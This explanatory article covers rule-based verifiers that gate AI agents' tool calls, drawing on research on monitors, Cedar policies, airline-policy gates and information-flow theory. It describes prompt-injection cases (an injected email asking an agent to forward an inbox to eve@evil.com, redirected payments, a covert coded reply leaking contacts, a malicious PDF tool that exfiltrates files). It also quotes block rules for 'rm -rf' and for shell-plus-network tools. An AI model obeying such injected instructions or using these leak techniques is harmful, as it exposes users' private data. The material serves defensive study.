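# Rule-based checks on AI agents' actions, and why they confuse ordinary task steps with violations

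## What a rule-based verifier for agents is

A rule-based verifier is a program that compares an AI agent's actions with fixed rules and returns a verdict, usually to allow or block an action. It doesn't use a language model to reach the verdict. Developers add these verifiers because agents now delete files, pay bills and send mail, and the model that chooses these actions sometimes chooses a bad one. The model may make a mistake, or it may follow instructions that an attacker has hidden in an email or a web page, an attack called prompt injection. The method is older than language models. *Safeguarding Mobile GUI Agent via Logic-based Action Verification* (Lee, Im and colleagues, 2025) adapts its verifier from runtime verification, a branch of software engineering in which a monitor compares a running program with a formal specification of correct behaviour.

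### Agents, tool calls and traces

An agent is a language model that carries out a task by taking actions in software. The model produces only data, so it writes a request for each action, and an ordinary program executes the request and returns the result. The model then uses that result to write its next request. Anthropic's programming guide *Computer use tool* calls this cycle the "agent loop". A verifier can check each request before the program executes it.

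Many requests are tool calls, which name a function and supply its arguments. In an example from the Model Context Protocol, a standard format for connecting models to tools, a request has the name `get_weather` and the argument "New York", and the response is a line of text with the temperature and cloud cover. Other requests are actions in a graphical interface. The agent receives a screenshot and then, according to Anthropic's *Build production agents with computer use*, clicks, types and scrolls as a person would. The data for such an action can be just `left_click` and the coordinates 640 and 60.

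A verifier can tell roughly what a call to `get_weather` will do from its name. But when an agent clicks on a pair of coordinates, the verifier has to use other information, such as the text on the screen or the state of the application, to work out what the click will do.

A trace, which some papers call a trajectory, is the record of one run from the user's request to the last result. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) defines it as the sequence of user messages, assistant messages, tool calls and tool results. The paper's monitors use only this sequence, so the model's internal reasoning does not affect the verdict.

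### Before the action, after it, or over the whole run

A typical rule has a trigger, a condition and a consequence. *AgentSpec* (2025), which introduced a small programming language for such rules, gives the example of a payment. If the agent starts a transaction (the trigger) and the amount is above some threshold (the condition), the user must confirm before the payment goes through (the consequence).

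Companies already sell this kind of checking. AWS announced one such product in March 2026 (*Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available*). It runs on a gateway outside the agent's own code. The gateway intercepts each request, checks it against the customer's policies before allowing access to the tool, and logs the decision, according to the product's documentation (*Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*). Customers can write a policy in plain English, which software then translates into Cedar, a formal policy language. A model may therefore help write a policy, but the gateway checks requests against the formal version.

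Checks can run before or after an agent acts, and Anthropic documents both kinds for its coding agent, Claude Code. The first kind runs after the model has written a tool call but before the tool runs. The checking script receives the tool's name and input, and it can allow the call, deny it or leave the decision to the user. The second kind runs after the tool has finished. It can still send the model a warning, but it is too late to prevent the tool from changing a file or sending a message. Under the usual settings, if the script for the first kind crashes or times out, the call goes ahead. Whoever installs the check has to turn on blocking for that case.

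Lee and colleagues describe the tradeoff between checking an action before and after it is taken. A check afterward can use more information, because the resulting screen shows what the action did, but it is too late to stop a payment or a message. A check beforehand can prevent the harm, but it requires predicting what the action will do, which can be as hard as choosing the action. The paper is about language models that review other models' actions, but a program has the same problem whenever the request does not state its effect.

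The remaining option is to check a finished run. Kekatos and colleagues did this by replaying thousands of recorded runs from public benchmarks through a monitor, without running any agent. The same recordings can be used to compare many sets of rules. Replay can also show whether an alarm would have come in time. Across 1,931 successful attacks on an agent built on GPT-4o, their general-purpose rules raised an alarm before the final harmful call in 52.4% of cases, only at that call in 17.7%, and not at all in 29.9%. Replay cannot show how the agent would have behaved after a block, since a live agent may try another route.

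### What "deterministic" promises

Papers and product pages often describe these verifiers as deterministic, which means that the same input always produces the same verdict. A language model acting as reviewer may give different verdicts on the same input. With a deterministic verifier, an auditor can rerun an old decision and get the same answer, and a developer can read the rule and work out beforehand what it will block. Deterministic verifiers also tend to be fast. The gate in *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) decides on each tool call in microseconds.

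*ToolGuardian* (Ravindran and Deochake, 2026) notes that "determinism is not the same as correctness". A wrong rule, a missing exception or an incomplete fact about a tool still leads to a wrong decision, and the verifier will repeat it whenever the same case comes up.

Yu and colleagues used a language model to turn written company policies into rules, and some of those rules blocked ordinary task steps. The clause "authenticate the user before any action" became a rule that blocked every tool, including the two that perform the authentication, until the user had authenticated, so no conversation could get past that point. Another rule required the user's confirmation for eight tools that only read data, so even looking up a flight's status would have needed approval.

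A rule can also work exactly as its author intended and still block a harmless action. Anthropic's documentation describes a script that denies any command containing `rm -rf`, which deletes a folder and everything in it without asking for confirmation. In the example, the script blocks the deletion of `/tmp/build`, which looks like a temporary folder that programmers routinely clear out. The script checks only for the characters `rm -rf`, so it would block the deletion of a folder of family photographs for the same reason.

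A rule-based verifier is also limited by its input. Two situations may differ in every way that matters to the user, but if the verifier receives the same data for both, it gives both the same verdict.

### Two runs that start the same way

Suppose a user asks an agent to send a travel itinerary to Dana. Here are two short traces that could follow.

| Step | Run A | Run B |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `find_file`: the itinerary | `find_file`: the itinerary |
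| 2 | `list_contacts`: returns every name and address | `list_contacts`: returns every name and address |
| 3 | `send_email`: the itinerary, to Dana's address | `send_email`: the whole contact list, to an outside address |

Run A is what the user wanted. Run B is a serious leak. Yet the two are identical up to and including step 2, so a deterministic verifier that checks step 2 before it happens must treat them alike. A rule against opening the contacts prevents the leak in run B and also makes run A impossible. A rule that permits it lets both runs continue. (A human reviewer with the same record would do no better at this point, because nothing in the record yet separates the runs.)

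They do differ at step 3, but only in the arguments. A rule that checks only the tool's name will again return the same verdict for both, while one that also checks the recipient or the contents could distinguish them. Waiting until after step 3 makes the leak easier to establish, but by then it is too late to prevent it.

Kekatos and colleagues describe a similar pair of runs in AgentDojo, a benchmark of prompt-injection attacks on agents. In both runs, the agent reads an inbox, looks up past transactions and sends money. In the legitimate run, the money goes to a supplier whose account number appears in the transaction history. In the other, it goes to an account number that appears only in an attacker's email. The final transfer alone is not enough to tell the runs apart.

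### The complaint against rules

The contacts example comes from *OS-Sentinel*, an October 2025 paper on agents that operate phones. Sun, Li and colleagues wrote that rule-based methods "struggle to scale and lack the contextual understanding" needed to separate harmless steps of a task from true violations. In their example, accessing the contacts to send an email is harmless, but leaking them is a violation.

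The claims about scale and context need separate evidence. The first is about how much new work each additional application or kind of risk requires. The second is about whether any rules strict enough to stop run B also wrongly stop run A. A verifier could be easy to extend and still confuse the two runs, or it could separate them perfectly in one email program and be useless everywhere else.

Both should be treated as claims to test. The sentence comes from the paper's introduction, where Sun and colleagues use it to motivate their own design, which combines a rule checker with a contextual judge (a model that assesses whether an action is acceptable in its situation). The work they cite there for rule-based verification, a system by Lee and colleagues, fits the description rather badly because its rules depend on the task. The system translates each user instruction into logical conditions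 before the agent starts. For example, an instruction to book tickets for a certain film at 7 pm becomes a rule that the title and the time must match before any booking goes through. Lee and colleagues reported up to 98.33% accuracy on 300 instructions in 18 mobile apps.

That figure does not refute the complaint, because the test measured whether actions matched the instruction, and an agent can leak data in ways that no instruction mentions. It does show that "rule-based" covers a wide range of verifiers, from a list of forbidden words to a logical formula checked against a whole run. The complaint could easily be true of word lists without being true of such formulas.

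### Counting the errors

A verifier can fail by missing a violation or by flagging a harmless run, and the usual measures weigh these errors differently. For example, a hypothetical verifier checks 1,000 runs, 50 of which actually contain violations.

| | True violations | Harmless runs | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Flagged | 40 | 190 | 230 |
| Not flagged | 10 | 760 | 770 |
| Total | 50 | 950 | 1,000 |

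The detection rate, also called recall, is the share of true violations that the verifier flags: 40 of 50, or 80%. The false-alarm rate is the share of harmless runs that it flags, here 190 of 950, or 20%. (Kekatos and colleagues call this the benign firing rate.) Precision is the share of flagged runs that are true violations, and it comes to only 40 of 230, about 17%. Accuracy is the share of all verdicts that are right: 800 of 1,000, or 80%. F1 combines precision *P* and detection rate *R* in a single number,

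F1 = 2*PR* / (*P* + *R*),

which is high only when both are high. Here it is about 0.29.

These numbers depend on the mix of runs as well as on the verifier. If the same verifier checked 500 violations and 500 harmless runs, with the same detection and false-alarm rates, its precision would rise from 17% to 80% and its F1 from 0.29 to 0.80, even though the verifier had not improved. Sun and colleagues' test set, MobileRisk, is also evenly split, with 102 unsafe runs and 102 safe ones. But it suits the question well because 51 of the safe runs are corrected versions of unsafe runs, much as run A is a corrected version of run B.

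A verifier that does nothing useful can also score well on accuracy or F1. One that never flags anything would score 95% accuracy on the runs in the table, and one that flags everything would score an F1 of 0.67 on an evenly split test set. The detection rate and the false-alarm rate together identify both verifiers, because both rates are 0% for the first and 100% for the second.

How much harm a false alarm does depends on what happens next. Sun and colleagues accept more false alarms because, they argue, a false alarm only causes a pause while someone checks, whereas a missed violation can cause irreversible loss. That argument holds when a person is there to respond, but if the verifier simply blocks the action, Dana never gets the itinerary. Even then, a false-alarm rate from recorded runs is only an estimate of the damage, as Kekatos and colleagues point out about their own figures.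 It counts the harmless runs that a live gate would have interrupted, but only running the agent again would show how many of those tasks would have failed.

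## How rules check single actions and changes to the system

Sun and colleagues criticize rules but also use them in their own system, OS-Sentinel. Its rule checker, the Formal Verifier, works only from the phone's files and the words on the screen. It does not use the user's instruction and has no rules for particular apps.

### Inside the Formal Verifier

At each step of a run, the verifier reads the text on the screen and the size, owner and last modification time of files in sensitive system directories. It then labels the step safe or unsafe, and a single unsafe step makes the whole run unsafe.

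To check the files, the verifier uses SHA-256, a standard function that converts data of any size into a short code called a hash. If the data changes, the hash is practically certain to change too. The verifier computes a hash of the file facts at each step and compares it with the hash from the next step. A mismatch means that something in the checked directories changed between the two steps, but the hash can't be used to tell which file changed or whether anyone had asked for the change.

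Two more checks search the screen text. The first looks for exact matches with a list of sensitive terms, which covers financial details, personal identifiers such as passport numbers, and security credentials such as two-factor codes. The second uses regular expressions, which match patterns instead of exact wording, to find email addresses, passwords, phone numbers and card numbers. For card numbers, the verifier also tests the checksum, a built-in relation between the digits that most random 16-digit numbers don't satisfy. Every match adds to a risk score, and a pattern match adds more than a keyword match.

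Slightly simplified, the verifier flags step *t* if

*h*(*t*) ≠ *h*(*t* + 1), or *w*₁*k* + *w*₂*p* > *θ*,

where *h* is the hash, *k* and *p* are the numbers of keyword and pattern matches, *w*₁ and *w*₂ are their weights, and *θ* is the threshold. The paper does not state the weights or the threshold.

The hash comparison can catch changes that don't appear in screenshots. In one of Sun and colleagues' recorded runs, an agent's step modified a system file with no visible sign on the screen. The verifier flagged the step because the hashes before and after it differed. A person or model reviewing only screenshots would have had no evidence of the change.

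However, the comparison can detect a change only after it has happened, because it needs the state after the step. It also treats every change alike, so it flags an agent for clearing an app's cache even when the user asked for that.

### The contacts runs on a phone

In both runs from the previous section, the user wants to send Dana an itinerary. Neither run needs to alter a system file, so we assume that the hashes match throughout and only the score matters. We also assume that a keyword match adds 1 point and a pattern match adds 3. These weights are invented, but the result does not depend much on them.

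At step 2, the Contacts app shows eight people, each with an email address and a phone number. That makes 16 pattern matches, or 48 points. At step 3 of run A, the draft email shows Dana's address and a hotel's phone number from the itinerary, for 6 points. In run B, if the agent pastes the contact list into the email, the screen shows all 16 details plus the outsider's address, for 51 points. If it attaches the list as a file, the screen shows only the outsider's address, for 3 points.

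| Step | Run A | Run B, list pasted | Run B, list attached |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2: contacts open | 48 | 48 | 48 |
| 3: email ready to send | 6 | 51 | 3 |

With a threshold of 20, the verifier flags step 2 in every run, including the harmless one. Letting step 2 through requires a threshold of at least 48. A pasted leak scores only 3 points more than an ordinary look at the contacts, and those points come from the outsider's address. The attached leak scores lower than the email to Dana, so no threshold can catch it at step 3 without also flagging run A.

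Adjusting the weights would not fix this, because the score measures how much sensitive text is on the screen, while the harm in run B depends on who receives that text. The pattern check, which produces nearly all of these points, also triggered most often per run in Sun and colleagues' data.

### Rules on tool calls

A tool call is easier to check than a screen, because the recipient of an email or a payment has a field of its own. *AgentSpec* uses such fields in rules with a trigger, a condition and a consequence. Here is its rule for bank transfers:

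```
rule @inspect_transfer
trigger Transfer
check !is_to_family_member
enforce user_inspection
end
```

The exclamation mark means "not". Before any transfer, the program checks whether the recipient is a family member, and if not, it asks the user to confirm. In the paper's example, a user regularly sends money to a son called Bob. The program allows a transfer to him without asking, but it asks for confirmation if the recipient is a new colleague also called Bob.

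AgentSpec's rule language is very small, and most of the checking in this rule happens inside `is_to_family_member`. Someone has to write that condition as an ordinary function, and it needs a reliable list of family members. Besides asking the user, a rule can stop the agent, run a preset action or prompt the agent's model to reconsider.

*AgentSpec* tested the approach on a robot agent doing household tasks. Without rules, the agent carried out up to 79% of the dangerous instructions, depending on the type of hazard. With rules, it carried out none, and its success on safe tasks fell only from 58.62% to 54.26%. One rule allowed the agent to pour only onto listed objects, such as houseplants. It prevented 96 risky scenarios, including pouring water on a laptop. Checking a rule's condition took one to three milliseconds, in runs that lasted 10 to 25 seconds.

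The researchers wrote these rules from descriptions of the risks in the benchmark, so the perfect score shows that rules can express known hazards precisely. It is weaker evidence that rules can catch hazards nobody has described. When a language model wrote the rules instead, some were much cruder. One banned all pouring, which stops an agent from pouring liquid on a laptop but also from watering houseplants.

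The results for an agent that writes and runs code were more mixed. The rules flagged over 90% of the risky programs. But the paper's category counts add up to 333 flagged programs, and the researchers judged 58 of them harmless. All 58 came from four of the 25 risk categories, where every flagged program was harmless. One of the four was "unsafe deserialization", which means rebuilding a program object from stored data. This can be dangerous if an attacker supplies the data, but these programs used their own fixed data. The rule correctly detected the risky operation but had no information about where the data came from.

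AgentSpec lets an action through unless a rule intervenes. The opposite default is to block everything that no rule permits, and Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, take this approach. A Progent rule names a tool and sets conditions on its arguments:

```
allow send_slack_msg when { to == "alice" }
```

For each call, Progent looks first for a matching "forbid" rule, then for an "allow" rule. If it finds neither, it blocks the call and returns an error message so that the agent can try something else. AgentSpec allows actions that no rule covers. A forgotten case can therefore let a harmful action through in AgentSpec or block a harmless one in Progent.

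The Slack rule comes from an example in which a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list that arrived by email. The list includes summarizing recent emails and posting the summary to the user's own Slack account, "alice". One of those emails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to `eve@evil.com`. The agent follows the instruction and calls `send_email`, but no rule allows that tool for this task, so the program blocks the call. The agent then posts the summary as planned.

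These rules fit only one task, so writing them by hand for every request would be impractical. Progent therefore has a language model draft them from the user's request and propose updates as the agent learns more. A separate program called a logic solver compares the old and new rules. If the new rules allow only calls that the old ones allowed, they take effect automatically. Otherwise, they need approval.

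Shi and colleagues cut the success rate of attacks on AgentDojo, the benchmark of prompt-injection attacks, from 39.9% to 1.0% while the agent kept its ability to do the tasks. The approver in that test accepted every request to widen the rules, as a careless user might. On a second benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%.

In the contacts example, Progent could let the agent open the contacts and then allow `send_email` only when `to` is Dana's address. Run A would finish, and run B would stop at step 3. If an attacker persuaded the agent to send the whole contact list to Dana, the same rule would allow it because it doesn't restrict the email's contents. More generally, Shi and colleagues say that Progent cannot stop attacks that use only permissions the task needs. For example, an attacker could trick a shopping agent into preferring one product over another without needing a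 forbidden tool.

### A commercial rule engine

The AWS gateway, whose rules are in Cedar, also blocks by default. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* gives the example of a refund tool with two requirements: only a user called John may process refunds, and only for $500 or less. With its long identifiers shortened, the rule looks like this:

```
permit (
  principal is OAuthUser,
  action == process_refund,
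  resource == refund-gateway
) when { username == "John" && amount < 500 };
```

The first three conditions check the kind of caller, the tool and the gateway the call passes through. The last line tests the caller's name and the amount in the tool call.

The rule permits only amounts below 500, so it blocks a refund of exactly $500, which the requirements allow John to make. Both `<` and `<=` are valid Cedar, so a syntax check would not reveal the error.

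A Cedar rule can use only the caller, the tool, the gateway and the tool's input values, according to AWS's *Schema constraints*, plus the current time, according to AWS's *Policy authoring guide*. The gateway takes the types of the input values from the tool's definition. The *Policy authoring guide* also says that a request goes through only if some rule permits it and no rule forbids it. A company could thus forbid emails to addresses outside its own domain. That would stop run B and allow run A if Dana is a colleague, but it would block both if Dana works elsewhere.

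Restricting the inputs to a Cedar rule also lets software analyze the rule formally and prove statements about every possible request, whereas ordinary testing covers only some requests. AWS has since added a compatible language, Dogwood, whose rules can also depend on what happened earlier in a session, as AWS's *Temporal policies* explains. InfoQ (2026) reports that rules with such conditions lose this formal analysis, which is why AWS made Dogwood a separate language. Similarly, Progent limits its conditions to simple comparisons on arguments, so a solver can compare two sets of rules, which would be much harder with AgentSpec's free-form functions.

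The gateway is outside the agent, so AWS describes it as a checkpoint that the model cannot get around. This holds only for calls that pass through the gateway, so a tool that the agent can reach another way needs its own protection.

### Gates that read the database

A checker cannot always tell from a call's arguments whether the call is allowed. A request to cancel booking 4417 looks the same whether or not the ticket is refundable, so the checker has to look up the booking.

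*Reason Less, Verify More* (Reddy, Challaram and Basu, 2026) examines this situation in the airline part of τ²-bench, a benchmark in which an agent handles requests from simulated customers. The agent receives the airline's policy as a document, but the tools do not enforce it. For example, the cancellation tool cancels any existing booking, even when the policy forbids it. The tool reports success, and the agent tells the customer that the cancellation went through. With GPT-4o mini, a small and cheap model, 78% of the observed failures were silent, meaning that the database ended up wrong although no tool had returned an error.

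Reddy and colleagues placed four checks, which they call gates, in front of the tools that change data. Each gate is a small function that reads the tool's name, its arguments and the current database, then allows the call or rejects it with a reason. The gate itself cannot change data.

In five attempts at each of 50 tasks, GPT-4o mini completed 42.0% of attempts correctly with the gates in place, compared with 29.6% without them. A second experiment with 15 new attempts per task gave almost the same gain, from 30.8% to 43.1%. The agent also became more consistent, as its chance of completing a task correctly five times in a row rose from 8% to 26%.

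Blocking actions helps an agent finish its tasks because the benchmark grades the final state of the database, and a forbidden cancellation permanently makes that state wrong. Most of the gains came from the 26 tasks in which at least one gate rejected a call, where success rose from 13.8% to 33.1%. On the other 24 tasks, it rose from 46.7% to 51.7%, a difference small enough to be chance.

The four gates differed greatly in quality. Reddy and colleagues audited them by counting a rejection as wrong if the benchmark's reference solution included the same call.

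| Gate | What it is meant to block | Rejections | Correct rejections |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cancellation eligibility | Cancellations that break the rules on fare, timing, insurance or flights already taken | 161 | 161 (100%) |
| Passenger count | Any change to the number of passengers | 9 | 9 (100%) |
| Read before write | Changes to a record that the agent has not looked up in this session | 90 | 70 (78%) |
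| Baggage allowance | Bag updates that charge wrongly for free bags or remove bags | 42 | 2 (5%) |

Forty of the baggage gate's 42 rejections were wrong, even though the database contained all the information needed for the check. Nearly all of the benefit came from the cancellation gate, the only one whose removal lowered the success rate. Removing any of the others, even the faultless passenger gate, raised it slightly. Those differences are small and may be noise, but a correct block does not guarantee that the agent will finish the task. In one task, the same gate blocked the agent repeatedly, and the agent never found a permitted alternative and failed all five attempts.

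The cancellation gate did best on a task in which the customer lies to get a forbidden cancellation. Agents handled this task correctly in 16 of 16 attempts with the gate, and in at most 1 in 16 without it. The gate checks the booking record, not the conversation, so a persuasive story doesn't affect the result.

GPT-5.2, a stronger model, also attempted forbidden changes, and the gates raised its success rate from 61.2% to 71.6%. This result comes from a single experiment with five attempts per task, and the confidence interval for the gain runs from almost zero to about 21 percentage points. On three tasks, the gates made GPT-5.2 do worse.

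Gates add little when the tools already enforce the rules. In the benchmark's retail part, a forbidden cancellation produces an error and changes nothing. Adding a set of gates there reduced successes from 40 to 37 of 64 attempts, mostly because a bug in one gate blocked corrected requests that the tool would have accepted. On another benchmark, BFCL, a simple gate that checked whether calls were well formed rejected nothing in 200 tests.

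Reddy and colleagues wrote their gates from the airline's policy and tested them on one set of tasks, so the gain on new tasks could be smaller. They also did not test whether reminding the model of the rules would have worked equally well.

### Reminders compared with enforcement

An earlier IBM study did make that comparison. In *Towards Enforcing Company Policy Adherence in Agentic Workflows*, Zwerdling, Boaz and colleagues (2025) used language models to turn a written policy into code that checks each tool call before it runs. The code can read the call's arguments, the conversation so far and the results of read-only tools. Before a booking, for example, it can count the passengers in the arguments and look up the number of free seats.

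They tested it on an earlier version of the same airline benchmark, using the 22 tasks where the customer asks for something the policy forbids. The agent had the policy document in its instructions in every condition. Adding the checking code raised its success rate from 45% to 68.5%, and its chance of succeeding in ten out of ten attempts from 22.7% to 50%. Showing the agent the policy again before every action and asking it to reconsider helped much less, raising the chance of ten successes to 27.3% at best.

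The best model's generated code passed an average of 82% of the 61 tests the researchers wrote by hand when a person had first matched the policy's clauses to the tools. When a model also did the matching, the code passed 75%. Because the code runs only when the agent is about to use a tool, it cannot catch an agent that fails to act when it should, such as one that refuses a cancellation the customer is entitled to.

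### Checking the tools themselves

All of these rules assume that a tool does what its description promises. ToolGuardian, the system that Ravindran and Deochake built, drops that assumption and checks tools before the agent may use them. Its rules are logical statements over a list of facts, for example:

```
deny(Tool) :- capability(Tool, shell_exec), network_access(Tool).
```

One rule is to reject any tool that can both run system commands and use the network. Ravindran and Deochake tested rules of this kind on 16 tools. Eight were harmless, and eight were malicious versions of real tools that kept the original descriptions. One of these converted PDF files as advertised but also sent their contents to an outside server.

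The test varied the evidence behind the facts. The first level used only the tools' descriptions. The second added a log of each tool's requests to the operating system, the third added the tool's observed behavior in a mock environment, and the fourth added an analysis of its source code.

| Evidence | Malicious tools rejected | Harmless tools rejected |
|---|---|---|
| Descriptions only | 5 of 8 | 5 of 8 |
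| + operating-system requests | 5 of 8 | 0 of 8 |
| + observed behavior | 6 of 8 | 0 of 8 |
| + source code | 7 of 8 | 2 of 8 |

With descriptions alone, the rules were no better than chance. They became much more useful when they were also based on what the tools did. Checking the source code exposed one more malicious tool, but also powerful functions in harmless ones. The rules rejected a legitimate tool for controlling a terminal because it can run programs and capture the screen, although these are roughly the normal functions of such a tool. Even at the best level of evidence, the rules gave all eight harmless tools only restricted admission.

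The choice of rule engine mattered less than the facts it was given. Ravindran and Deochake also gave those facts to a simple scoring program and a language model, and when the facts included observed behavior, all three methods were 88% accurate.

ToolGuardian also checks individual calls while the agent works, and these checks classified all 20 scenarios correctly. The paper acknowledges that the researchers designed the scenarios and the rules together, so the perfect score mainly shows that the rules work as intended.

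### Conditions a program can read

The rules that worked well in these studies each state the forbidden condition in terms of data that the checker has. The cancellation gate needs the fare, the booking time, the insurance and the flights already taken, all of which are in the airline's database. The Slack rule needs one argument of one call, and the pouring rule needs the name of an object and a list. Reddy and colleagues call such policies "state-decidable", meaning that the current data and the arguments of the call are enough to decide whether the call breaks the policy. They exclude policies that require legal interpretation or human judgment.

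Zwerdling and colleagues include this test in their method. Before generating any code, a language model assesses whether the arguments, the conversation and earlier tool calls contain enough information to check each clause of the policy. If they do not, the system sets the clause aside for a human expert. A developer who writes rules by hand could do the same to find out early which parts of a policy a program cannot enforce.

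*Beyond Suspicious Steps* (2026) ran AgentSpec with rules that did not match the violations it was looking for. The three default rules covered destructive file deletion, data uploads and access to system files, but the study was looking for violations such as an agent gradually drifting from its role or rewriting its own goal. An agent can do either without doing anything those rules cover.

A rule needs the right data, but having it does not make the rule correct. The baggage gate had a complete database and was wrong 95% of the time. Errors like that are relatively easy to fix, because a developer can compare the rule with the policy and correct it once for all future runs. A missing fact is harder to fix. A checker can compare an email's recipient with Dana's address, but nothing in the call records that Dana is the person the user had in mind.

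## Why the same step can be harmless or a violation

When a verifier lacks the fact that decides whether a run is harmless, some of its verdicts must be wrong, however carefully its rules are written. A short calculation gives the minimum number of errors.

### The smallest possible error

Let *o* be everything the verifier receives about a run when it decides, such as the tool's name, its arguments or the earlier steps. A deterministic verifier maps each *o* to "allow" or "block", so two runs with the same *o* get the same verdict.

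Let *P*(*o*, harmless) be the share of all runs that produce *o* and are harmless, and let *P*(*o*, violation) be the share that produce *o* and are violations. If the verifier allows *o*, it is wrong about every violation in that group. If it blocks *o*, it is wrong about every harmless run in the group. The best it can do is to make the smaller of these two errors. Adding up over all observations gives

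error ≥ Σₒ min(*P*(*o*, harmless), *P*(*o*, violation)).

Statisticians call the right-hand side the Bayes error. Tossing a coin for each run does not get below it, because the result then lies somewhere between the two errors. Replacing the rules with a language model or a person doesn't help either, as long as the replacement receives only *o*. (A colleague who happens to know the user has more than *o*.)

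Suppose the verifier's only information about each of 1,000 runs is "read contacts, send email". Of these runs, 990 are harmless and 10 are leaks. Allowing them all misses the 10 leaks, and blocking them all stops the 990 harmless runs. The lowest possible error rate is therefore 1%, which the verifier achieves by blocking nothing. If a missed leak is more than 99 times as bad as an interrupted task, blocking everything is better, but the 990 harmless tasks still fail.

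Now suppose the verifier also receives the recipient's address. In this invented example, 950 of the harmless emails and 1 of the leaks go to someone in the user's contacts. The other 40 harmless emails and 9 leaks go to unknown addresses. The minimum number of errors is still 10, because harmless emails outnumber leaks in both groups. But the verifier can now block only emails to unknown addresses, which catches 9 of the 10 leaks and stops 40 harmless emails. Without the recipient's address, reliably catching any leak meant stopping all 990 harmless emails.

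A further detail, whether the email contains the contact list, splits the runs again:

| Recipient | Contact list in the email | Harmless runs | Leaks | Verdict with fewest errors | Errors |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| In the contacts | No | 945 | 0 | Allow | 0 |
| In the contacts | Yes | 5 | 1 | Allow | 1 |
| Unknown | No | 38 | 0 | Allow | 0 |
| Unknown | Yes | 2 | 9 | Block | 2 |

The minimum is now 3 errors. An extra detail can never raise the minimum, because the verifier can ignore the detail and give both parts of a group the old verdict. The calculation assumes a fixed mix of runs, but an attacker who knows the rule can change the mix, for example by first getting an address into the user's contacts.

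A real verifier can also make many more errors than its input makes unavoidable. OS-Sentinel's Formal Verifier scores every address on the screen alike, even the recipient's. Sun and colleagues define contextual risks, such as privacy leaks, as risky behavior visible in the recorded screens and actions, so for these risks, part of the trouble is that the rules discard information they already have. When their contextual judge works step by step, it receives only the current screen and the agent's action. At step 2 these are the same in run A, where Dana gets the itinerary, and in run B, where an outsider gets the contact list, so the judge can't distinguish the two runs at that step.

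### What a monitor can enforce

In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider worked out which policies a program can enforce by monitoring another program's steps and stopping it when it is about to break a policy. Firewalls, most operating-system checks, and a gate in front of an agent's tools all work this way. Schneider's argument barely changes if the mechanism instead replaces the forbidden step with an acceptable one, such as an error message.

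Such a mechanism can enforce a policy only if three conditions hold:

- Each run is acceptable or unacceptable by itself, regardless of what other runs do.
- Once a partial run is unacceptable, no continuation can make it acceptable again.
- Every unacceptable run becomes unacceptable after a finite number of steps.

Policies that meet all three conditions are called safety properties. Informally, they require that some particular bad thing never happens. "Never email an address outside the company" is a safety property because the bad thing is a single identifiable call. "Answer every customer eventually" is not, because the answer could still come no matter how long a customer has waited. Adding a deadline makes it a safety property, since a run violates the policy once the deadline passes without an answer. Monitors can enforce only safety properties, and there are some that no monitor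 can enforce.

The condition on continuations limits which rules a developer can enforce about the contacts. Suppose a developer writes, "The agent may open the contacts only if it then emails the person the user named." After step 2 of run A, the agent has opened the contacts but not yet sent anything, so the run would break the policy if it ended there. A monitor has no information about later steps, so to enforce this policy strictly it must block step 2, which also prevents the email that would have justified the step. The developer has to move the condition to a later step, for instance by forbidding the agent to send contact details to anyone the user did not name.

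Schneider represents a policy as a small machine that changes state as the run proceeds. One example forbids sending messages after reading a file. The machine starts in a state called "no file read", which allows every action. When the program first reads a file, the machine moves to a state called "file read", which allows everything except sending. A developer could adapt this to agents by replacing "read a file" with "open the contacts". The resulting rule is easy to enforce and would stop run B, but it would also stop run A, along with almost every email whose address the agent had to look up.

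An enforceable policy can still be a bad one. Schneider points out that enforcing a stricter policy than intended also enforces the intended one, but may forbid harmless runs or, in the extreme case, every run.

### Why leaks involve more than one run

In the contacts example, the user wants outsiders to learn nothing from the contact list. A strict formal version of this requirement is noninterference, under which secret inputs have no effect on what outsiders can observe. Clarkson and Schneider (2009), in *Hyperproperties*, express it as a condition on all the runs a system can produce. For every run *t*, there must be a run *t′* with no secret inputs but the same publicly visible events. The system leaks if removing the secrets would have changed what outsiders see.

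An agent opens the user's contacts and then emails a conference organizer the words "Friday works". In one version, the agent needed the organizer's address, and the user had already chosen Friday. In another, an attacker has told the agent to write "Friday" if a certain doctor is in the contacts and "Monday" if not. Both versions can produce the same two tool calls, and the email contains no name, address or phone number. The email leaks information about the contacts if different contacts would have changed what the agent wrote.

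Noninterference depends on a fact about another run, so it does not meet Schneider's first condition. Clarkson and Schneider call a policy on sets of runs a hyperproperty, and they argue that information flow is tied to "correlations between (not within) executions". In their framework, the rule against writing to the network after reading a file is a policy on single runs, unlike noninterference.

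A monitor that checks one run at a time therefore can't enforce noninterference exactly. According to Schneider, monitors meant to prevent information flow enforce something stricter, which guarantees no flow but also rules out harmless runs. A ban on all email after opening the contacts would stop both the attacker's coded message and the honest "Friday works". In the theory, the false alarms come from using a policy on single runs in place of a policy on sets of runs.

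Blocking can even create a leak. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that outputs 0, 1 or the value of a secret bit, choosing freely among the three. Its possible outputs are the same whatever the secret is. Removing some of its behaviors so that it always outputs the secret makes it leak, even though every remaining run was already possible. By contrast, removing runs can never cause a violation of a safety property.

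Noninterference also causes false alarms. Taken literally, it rejects run A. If the contacts had listed a different address for Dana, the itinerary would have gone there, so the secret list affects what outsiders can observe. A usable policy needs authorized exceptions, which security researchers call declassification.

A developer can get around the limit on single runs by monitoring several. Finkbeiner, Hahn and colleagues (2018), in *Monitoring Hyperproperties*, study how to do this with HyperLTL, a logic whose formulas can refer to more than one run. For the conference email, a developer could run the agent in a sandbox with the doctor in the contacts, run it again without the doctor, and compare the messages. This requires at least one extra run per check. The model's wording may also vary between runs even when the contacts are the same, so a difference between two emails would be weak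 evidence of a leak until the developer had repeated the comparison several times.

### "Only for this purpose"

People often explain the difference between runs A and B by purpose, saying that the agent may use the contacts only to send the itinerary. Privacy policies contain many rules of this kind. For example, American hospitals may use medical records for treatment and billing but not for gossip.

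To check such a rule, a program needs a definition of when an action is *for* a purpose. *Formalizing and Enforcing Purpose Restrictions in Privacy Policies* (Tschantz, Datta and Wing, 2012) defines this through planning. An action is for a purpose if it belongs to a plan that achieves the purpose as well as possible and has no steps that could be removed without making the plan less effective. The action doesn't have to succeed, so a medical test that finds nothing can still be for diagnosis.

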